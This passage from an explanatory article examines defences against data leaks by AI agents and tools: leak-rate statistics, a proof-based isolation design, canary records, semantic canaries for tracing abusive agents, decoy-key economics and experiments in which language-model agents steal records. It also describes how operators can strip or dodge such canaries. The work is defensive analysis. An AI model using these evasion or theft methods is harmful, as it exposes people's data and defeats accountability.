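Even that may be too generous. With only a signature check, the tools themselves leaked in 108 runs, or 36 cases if the repeats always agreed. In the other 15 cases, the tool had leaked nothing even without the stronger defences, so finding no leaks in those cases is weak evidence that disposable copies work. The limit also rises for a single kind of attack, just as *Exploring the scientific underpinnings of investigating safety signals* applies the same rule to subgroups of patients, such as one age group.

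| What counts as an independent test | Number with no leaks | 95% upper limit |
|---|---|---|
| Every run | 153 | 1.9% |
| Every case | 51 | 5.7% |
| Every case in which the tool leaked with only a signature check | 36 | 8.0% |
| Every case of the basic attack that carries data between calls | 5 | 45% |

These limits apply only to attacks like those tested. The researchers wrote the 51 cases themselves, so the cases are not a random sample of the malicious tools that the payroll office might install. A different kind of attack could succeed every time, even if every figure in the table is correct.

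*Systematic reviews of adverse effects* recommends asking how thoroughly the researchers looked for harm, how many patients they studied and for how long. Duration is easy to overlook when testing software. Aun and colleagues also tried a short decoy test on their 52 malicious versions, with three calls to each tool, and flagged only 28. Many of the others were triggered only by a later call or particular content. Rerunning the same three calls from the start would not have caught a tool triggered by the fourth.

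For leaks that do occur at random, the office needs 299 independent sessions with no leaks to put the upper limit on the leak rate below 1%. If it runs only 20, a tool that leaks in 1% of sessions has an 82% chance of passing. These figures apply only to a closed test, where the team records every way data can leave. Finding no leaked canaries in ordinary use is much weaker evidence that a tool doesn't leak.

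### What the proof adds

Aun and colleagues also proved mathematically that their design prevents this kind of leak. The proof applies to any signed tool, including one with an attack that nobody has thought of, and to data in an encoding that the detector can't read. It shows that the contents of a request depend only on what its destination may receive, apart from public details of the call and the fixed time and random seed that the system supplies. Running more tests could never establish this, but the proof depends on several assumptions:

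- The tool can communicate only through the broker, and nobody uses the timing of requests to carry information.
- The clean process contains no user data when the system copies it.
- The operating system, the broker, the signature check and the policy are all correct.
- The details that every copy receives, such as file names, contain no secrets.
- The system treats any reply from a server as if it might contain everything that server is allowed to know.

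A mistake in the policy would be enough to cause a leak. If somebody in the payroll office labelled the salary file as public, the system would follow the policy and send the file to any server allowed to receive public data. Information can also leak through timing, although running the copies one at a time reduced the measured leakage between them from about 38–48 bits a second to at most 0.61.

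The proof describes a design, so a programming error could still break one of its assumptions. The 153 runs tested the program itself and provide some evidence against such an error. The researchers also tested the assumptions directly. For example, they wrote tools that opened a hidden channel between copies during start-up, and the system refused to run them.

The defence also requires the office to run the tool itself. The office can't make copies of a tool on another company's server, so it has to assume that every reply may contain anything the tool is allowed to access. In one test, this assumption stopped a harmless remote tool's output from reaching a public site in all three attempts, although ordinary labels would have allowed two of them.

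Even with a local tool, the protection ends once data reaches the permitted server, as it does with information-flow labels, so the office still needs canaries to trace the data after that.

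## What canaries miss

A canary can trace the salary file only if the fake employee travels with the real ones and somebody then finds or uses it.

### When the secret is reworded

Suppose Ruth Adeyemi, a buyer in the Leeds office, complains about her pay, and her director asks an agent to write to an outside adviser about it. The agent reads the Leeds pages of the salary file, which include the fake employee 2B9X-64035-TW. What it learns about Ruth could leave in several forms:

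```
Records     Ruth Adeyemi | 5D2K-38164-RV | Buyer              | £52,400
            Colin Marsh  | 8F7C-20593-HN | Purchasing manager | £49,800
Summary     Ruth Adeyemi is a buyer on about £52,000.
Inference   She earns more than her manager.
```

The last line discloses something confidential about two people without including a name, a figure or a canary. The adviser knows who "she" is from the rest of the message. However thoroughly the gateway decodes and normalises the sentence, it will find no match, because the agent had no reason to mention the fake employee. A language model acting as a judge might detect the disclosure, but it would also raise some false alarms, and it could work only while the office can read the message.

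Some inferences require combining several harmless-looking messages. If ten people in a team earn £41,000 on average, and the average rises to £42,500 when an eleventh joins, the newcomer earns £57,500 (11 × £42,500 − 10 × £41,000). Neither message would contain a staff number or anyone's individual salary.

A fake employee can leave a trace in an average. In a team of 24 real people and one fake, adding £250 to the fake salary raises the average by £10. If each recipient's copy gives the fake employee a different salary, an exact average could identify the copy it came from. The trace disappears if somebody rounds the average to the nearest hundred pounds, or removes the fake employee before calculating it, as the office has to do when it compiles statistics.

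### Canaries made of meaning

*Who Owns This Agent?* describes a much fuller attempt to make canaries that survive rewording, although it is about tracing agents, not data. When an AI agent harasses a company's customers, the company can see the messages but not the account behind them. The vendor that hosts the agent's language model knows every account, but can't tell which session is producing the harassment. If the company puts a canary in something the agent will read, the vendor can search its logs for that canary to find the session and its account.

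The vendor searches for lexical canaries by exact or normalised matching and for semantic ones with a classifier. A semantic canary, such as a caller's anger, can survive transcription and paraphrase even if none of the caller's words do.

But many callers are angry, so one such property identifies nobody. The method therefore uses a secret combination:

1. An authorised investigator, such as a police unit or a platform's abuse team, lists *n* properties that would be ordinary in the conversation or on the web page.
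2. The investigator picks *k* of them at random, keeps the choice secret, and has a language model work them into content that the agent will read.
3. The investigator notes when the agent reads the content, then sends the *k* properties and a narrow time window to the model vendors.
4. Each vendor checks every session that was active in that window and returns those that show at least *m* of the *k* properties.

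Requiring fewer than all *k* allows for some to get lost, but it also lets in more innocent sessions. Suppose each property occurs naturally in 20% of sessions, independently of the others. The chance that an innocent session shows at least four of five is:

```
exactly four    5 × 0.2⁴ × 0.8 = 0.00640
all five        0.2⁵           = 0.00032
total                            0.00672
```

The four-of-five test produces about 67 false matches in 10,000 sessions. Requiring eight of nine planted properties reduces that to about 0.2, because the chance of a false match falls to 9 × 0.2⁸ × 0.8 + 0.2⁹, or about 0.000019. The stricter rule also misses more real matches. If each planted property has a 90% chance of surviving and being recognised, a marked session passes the four-of-five test 92% of the time and the eight-of-nine test 77%.

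A dishonest operator can put a filter between the outside world and the model, so the researchers also set conditions for the list of properties. The list has to be long so that the operator can't guess the secret selection. The properties should be about equally common and look ordinary in context. Each should also carry information the agent needs, so that removing it makes the agent worse at its job. To check how common the properties were, the researchers had Claude look for each one in 500 ordinary items, then discarded the rarest and the most frequent.

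### How well they worked

The researchers tested the method in three settings. In the first, they generated 200,000 synthetic 12-turn conversations with canaries chosen from 30 writing habits, and used a probe on a model's internal activity to look for these habits. In the second, they planted properties such as layout, purpose and style in 10,000 real web pages from Common Crawl, a public archive of the web, and trained a small text classifier to recognise these properties. In the third, an agent running on Qwen 3.5-9B tried to break into 15 purpose-built websites and recover a hidden code from each, while reading pages that contained canaries.

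Lexical canaries worked well when nobody tried to remove them. The vendor's search recovered every reference code planted in a conversation and every random identifier planted in a server's response. On web pages, the software an agent used to extract the text could remove the canary. When a language model did the extraction, visible canaries still came through in over 60% of cases, though the paper shows this only for the top eight of 30 canaries. In the hacking tests, filenames and visible text survived better than metadata and hidden fields.

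The table gives the results for semantic canaries when the researchers planted five properties. In the third column, a language model rephrased everything the agent read. In the fourth, the operator knew the full list of possible properties and rewrote any that appeared.

| Setting and rule | Found with no attack | Found after rephrasing | Found after targeted rewriting | False matches in unmarked sessions |
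|---|---|---|---|---|
| Web pages, 4 of 5 | 96.9% | 96.2% | 93.9% | 10.6% |
| Conversations, 3 of 5 | 96.4% | 83.1% | 19.2% | 1.5% |
| Hacking sessions, 4 of 5 | 96.4% | 92.9% | 71.4% | 3.6% |

Rephrasing would have destroyed most lexical canaries, so these are good results. Targeted rewriting was best at removing the property from conversations, probably because each habit appeared in only one message. A web page repeats its purpose in the headings, menus and text, so a rewrite that misses one of these leaves the property in place.

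The false-match results are less encouraging. Under a four-of-five rule, the calculation above predicts a false-match rate of 0.67%, but the measured rate was about five times as high in hacking sessions and 16 times as high on web pages. One reason could be that the properties were more common than the assumed 20%. In unmarked hacking sessions, the detectors found an average of 6.3 of the 28 properties, or 22.5%, but that would give a false-match rate of only about 1.1% if the properties were independent. The rest of the gap probably arises because properties occur together. For example, a page that looks like a login form is also likely to be short and formal. The hacking-session figure is rough because it comes from only 150 unmarked sessions. In conversations, the false-match rate was lower than the 5.8% predicted for a three-of-five rule.

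The detection rates may also be inflated because the marked web pages and hacking sessions were longer than the unmarked ones, which gave the detectors more text to find each property in. The researchers did not repeat the test with texts of equal length.

Evading detection made the results worse, as intended. With nine properties planted in each conversation, targeted rewriting reduced detection from 100% to 84.7%, but it also more than doubled the length of the messages and lost about a quarter of their names and numbers. In the hacking tests, rewriting cut the agent's success rate from 39% to 17% with six planted properties, and from 31% to 9% with seven. But the agent succeeded 46% of the time on unmarked pages, so the canaries themselves may have made the task harder.

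An operator who also knew *k* and *m* could avoid detection by dropping every session that contained *m* properties from the full list. Since ordinary sessions contain them too, this discarded 84% of unmarked conversations at the setting the researchers highlighted, 46% of web pages and 43% of hacking sessions.

### Using semantic canaries to trace data

The payroll office could borrow the method, but it would lose most of the advantages that made it work.

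The first is the time window: a vendor that knows when an agent read the canary has to check only the sessions active around that moment. With nine properties planted in each conversation and six required for a match, the search found 79% of marked conversations and wrongly matched 0.20% of the others. In a window with 500 sessions, that is one false match, which somebody can review. But stolen salary data could appear anywhere, months later. If the office applied the same test to three million documents, it would expect 6,000 false matches. Even if it required eight of the nine properties and used the optimistic figures, it would expect 57.

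The method also requires the vendor to have logs to search and to cooperate. An office that insists on zero data retention has asked its model host not to keep those logs. A dishonest broker has no reason to help, and the researchers exclude compromised vendors from their analysis.

In the tests, the properties only had to reach the model's input, but a leak may consist of the model's output after the information has been summarized once or twice. A summary such as "She earns more than her manager" could reveal protected information, but it is too short to contain four of the five properties.

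A thief who wants salaries also loses little by evading canaries. The thief needs only the real figures and can discard everything else in the file, whereas a scam agent has to understand its victim's messages and so can't easily discard their meaning. The office can't alter the salary figures without paying people the wrong amount.

Semantic canaries suit prose better. Suppose the office sends several consultants a confidential report on why staff are leaving. In each copy, it can vary the order of the causes, the branch used as an example and the objection answered first. Ten choices with two options each give 1,024 versions. A paraphrase that keeps the argument will probably keep several of these choices, but a one-paragraph summary will not.

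The office can then tell recipients apart only if a leak rarely matches the wrong version. When the researchers planted nine properties and required five to match, a conversation matched a different secret combination 1.9% of the time. At that rate, if the errors were independent, a report leaked by one of 20 consultants would have about a 30% chance of also matching at least one of the other 19. A semantic match is therefore a reason to look at a recipient's records, but the office would need something else to confirm the source, such as a lexical canary in the same document or a row in the ledger.

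### When the real data leaves by itself

Even a leak that copies records word for word may contain no canary. If the director asks an agent what Ruth earns, the agent retrieves only Ruth's record, so anything it sends will include none of the fake employees the office has planted, no matter how many there are.

Thieves also choose which rows to take. If ten of a file's thousand rows are fake employees, 20 rows taken at random have about an 18% chance of including at least one. But a thief who takes the 20 rows with the highest salaries will get none, because the office gave its fake employees unremarkable pay so that ordinary filters wouldn't remove them.

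Legitimate processing can also remove canaries. A tool that matches the payroll against the pension scheme's membership list will drop the fake employees because they aren't members. The office also removes them before it runs the payroll, so the payslips and the file of bank payments never contain canaries. Those documents hold the same salaries, and a leak from them would go unnoticed.

The office can reduce the problem by planting canaries where a selective thief would look. *WiP* describes an experiment that used lucrative fake loans this way. A fake buyer at the top of the buyers' pay range would catch somebody collecting the best-paid buyers' records. A fake director probably would not work, because anyone interested in the directors' pay is likely to know who the directors are.

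For small and well-known groups, searching for the real data makes more sense. The gateway can store keyed hashes of real names paired with their salaries, then check outgoing messages for the same pairs. It can find any record that leaves in its original form, including Ruth's. But a real salary is weaker evidence of where a leak came from than a canary, because Ruth, her bank and her landlord may all have a copy. Information-flow labels can also stop Ruth's record, even if it is reworded, provided the system has tracked what the agent read.

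### When thieves recognise a canary

A thief who suspects that some of the keys in a stolen file are decoys can check them before using them. Checking may set off an alert, as it did at Grafana Labs, but the thief can recognize some decoys by their features without setting one off. Security researchers call this fingerprinting. *Calibrated Bait* (Gans, 2026) cites a 2018 study by Vetterl and Clayton that used fingerprinting to identify 7,605 decoy computers on the internet.

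Weinberg warns that a scanner's users can tune it to flag keys whose randomness or naming differs from an organisation's real ones. Chauhan and Revankar address this by fitting a model of character patterns to real credentials of each format and generating decoys from it. They then test whether a statistical classifier can distinguish the decoys from real keys. A privacy setting limits how much any one real key can influence the model, since a decoy that reproduced part of a real key would be worse than no decoy. They note that passing these tests doesn't prove the decoys are indistinguishable from real keys.

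People can also give canaries away. Grafana Labs recommends ordinary names such as `AWS_API_CREDS` over `CANARY_TOKEN_AWS`. It also discusses whether to tell staff about canaries. Several of its employees set them off by looking around before the company announced them. Announcing canaries reduces such accidents, but a dishonest employee, or an intruder who has reached the company wiki, can read a list posted there.

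Gans analyses how a defender's best strategy changes when an intruder might be able to check whether a key is a decoy before using it. The defender in the model gains when the intruder uses a decoy and loses when the intruder uses a real key. If detection is valuable enough, the defender wants to add decoys until the intruder is only just willing to try a key. But an intruder who is that unsure has the most to gain from checking.

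Suppose a company has 100 real keys and 100 decoys, and a different thief finds each one. A real key is worth £1,000 to a thief, and using a decoy costs the thief £1,000 by exposing the theft. If the keys are mixed together, half are decoys, so using an unchecked key gains a thief nothing on average. When checking is too expensive, the thieves are barely willing to use what they find, so they use all 100 real keys and trigger all 100 decoys.

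Now suppose a new tool lets a thief check a key for £200 without setting off an alert. A checked key has a 50% chance of being real and worth £1,000, so checking is worth £500 − £200, or £300. Every thief would check, and nobody would trigger a decoy. The company can prevent this only by mixing in fewer decoys. If one key in five is a decoy, using a key unchecked is worth 0.8 × £1,000 − 0.2 × £1,000, or £600. Checking first is worth 0.8 × £1,000 − £200, which is also £600, so thieves have no reason to check.

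If one key in five is a decoy, there are 25 decoys among the 100 real keys. The other 75 decoys have to be kept separately, where thieves will assume that everything is bait and leave it alone. The company now gets 25 alerts instead of 100, while thieves still use all 100 real keys. Anyone who judged the danger by the number of alerts would think thefts had fallen by three-quarters. This can happen even if nobody checks a key, because the ability to check is enough.

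Gans finds that if checking is cheap, the defender may do better to use decoys as a deterrent. With the same numbers, if nine keys out of ten are decoys, checking them isn't worth a thief's time, because the average return from checking a key is £100 and the check costs £200. This takes a lot of decoys, and it produces no alerts if it works. *A Game-Theoretic Taxonomy and Survey of Defensive Deception for Cybersecurity and Privacy* (2017) describes a model in which the ability to detect decoys always helps the attacker but sometimes helps the defender too.

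The model assumes that both sides know the costs and proportions, which no real company does, but its warning about alerts applies more generally. A team whose canaries stop producing alerts should compare that drop with something a thief's caution doesn't affect, such as unexplained uses of its real keys. The fake employees in the salary file are harder for a thief to identify, because no service can be used to check whether a staff number is genuine and the thief would have to look each person up.

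### Decoys beside the path

An attacker can also miss a decoy without suspecting anything. Ghifiardi (2026), in *Optional Traps*, set a small language model to steal records from a mock service. A debugging page leaked a working key, and in two sessions the service also contained decoys, including a backup file with a canary key. In both, the agent read the working key from the debugging page and exported the records in six requests, without opening a decoy. It already had what it needed, so it had no reason to explore. Two sessions prove little about how often this happens.

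With one real key and one canary, Chauhan and Revankar's formula would give the agent about a 50% chance of touching the canary, but the formula doesn't apply when a thief finds the real key first.

Ghifiardi then moved the bait to where the agent was already looking. Another small model had 20 sessions in each of three versions of the service, with instructions that told it where to look:

| Debugging page | Sessions in which the agent exported the records | Sessions in which the service cut the agent off |
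|---|---|---|
| Leaks the real key | 20 | 0 |
| Removed | 0 | 0 |
| Supplies a canary key | 0 | 19 |

Closing the leak prevented every theft, with or without the canary. The canary identified the attacker and cut off its access. In the remaining session, the agent read the page with the canary but tried a different key that didn't work, so it triggered no canary alert.

Bait placed on the path can also catch legitimate agents that use the same path. In a later experiment with several agents, one had the correct key in its instructions but fetched the debugging page anyway, used the canary it found there instead, and lost its access. Ghifiardi recommends short, reversible penalties for this reason. The service in the tests blocked an agent for 15 minutes.

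Tracebit's *ARTEX keeps changing. It still hits canaries* reports a very different result. The company ran ARTEX, the attack tool that Dragos saw in November, 59 times in Amazon's cloud. Every run touched a canary, most within five minutes. Tracebit sells canaries and chose where to put them, so the result probably overstates how well they work. But it doesn't contradict Ghifiardi's, because a tool that searches an account for anything useful will come across decoys that an agent with a shorter route would pass by.

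A thief looking for salaries may never open a decoy file called `passwords.txt` in the next folder. A fake employee in the salary file avoids this problem, because anyone who copies the whole file takes the fake entry too.

### When nothing happens

All these failures look the same to the security team because none of them triggers an alert. The more likely a theft is to trigger an alert, the more reassuring it is not to receive one.

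Suppose 1% of the records in a large database contain live canaries, a thief copies 100 records at random, and each stolen canary has a 30% chance that somebody will use it. Any one copied record then has a 0.01 × 0.3, or 0.3%, chance of raising an alarm. For the whole theft:

`chance of detection = 1 − (1 − 0.003)¹⁰⁰ ≈ 26%`

The 30% is an assumption, but not an unusually pessimistic one. *Rethinking Cyber Deception for AI Attackers* (hrbrmstr, 2026) cites a study by the security company Horizon3.ai in which human testers took the bait about 37% of the time.

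Suppose the team thought there was a 10% chance that such a theft had taken place. Out of 1,000 companies in the same position, 100 would have had a theft. Canaries would reveal 26 of these and miss 74. The 900 companies with no theft would also get no alert, so 74 of the 974 companies without an alert, or 7.6%, would have lost data. The lack of an alert would lower the team's estimate from 10% to 7.6%, which would hardly justify closing an investigation.

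The table shows how the result changes with the assumptions. Each row alters only what it mentions.

| Situation | Chance of detecting the theft | Suspicion left after silence |
|---|---|---|
| As above | 26% | 7.6% |
| A thief tries either all the stolen canaries or none | 19% | 8.3% |
| Somebody uses every stolen canary | 63% | 3.9% |
| 5% of records contain canaries | 78% | 2.4% |
| The thief copies 1,000 records | 95% | 0.5% |

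The second row is probably more realistic than the first. Whether a thief tries keys depends largely on habit, so ten stolen canaries don't give ten independent chances of an alert. Nor are two months of silence twice as reassuring as one, because a thief who ignored the keys in October may well ignore them in November.

The third row shows how far waiting alone can lower the team's suspicion. Waiting longer may give a thief more time to use a canary, but about 37% of these thefts contain no canary, so the suspicion can't fall below 3.9%. Only more canaries, or better places for them, would lower that limit. A fivefold increase helps a great deal, but in the payroll office it would mean inventing roughly 50 employees for every thousand real ones.

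These figures also assume that a used canary always reaches the team as an alert. Grafana Labs warns that a company loses all visibility if its monitoring fails or an intruder takes it over. It also advises acknowledging each alert quickly, because Thinkst's platform groups later alerts with an unacknowledged one, and the team may miss a second intruder at a different address. A 5% chance that the alerts weren't working roughly doubles the suspicion in the last row, from 0.5% to 1.1%. Setting off a few canaries on purpose every month is an easy way to reduce that risk.

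If a company's main worry is that a competitor might simply read its salary data, the 30% in the calculation could be close to zero, and the absence of an alert would then leave the suspicion at almost exactly 10%. Searching for lexical canaries in places where stolen data appears covers some of these cases, but it can't find a file that a competitor keeps on a private server.
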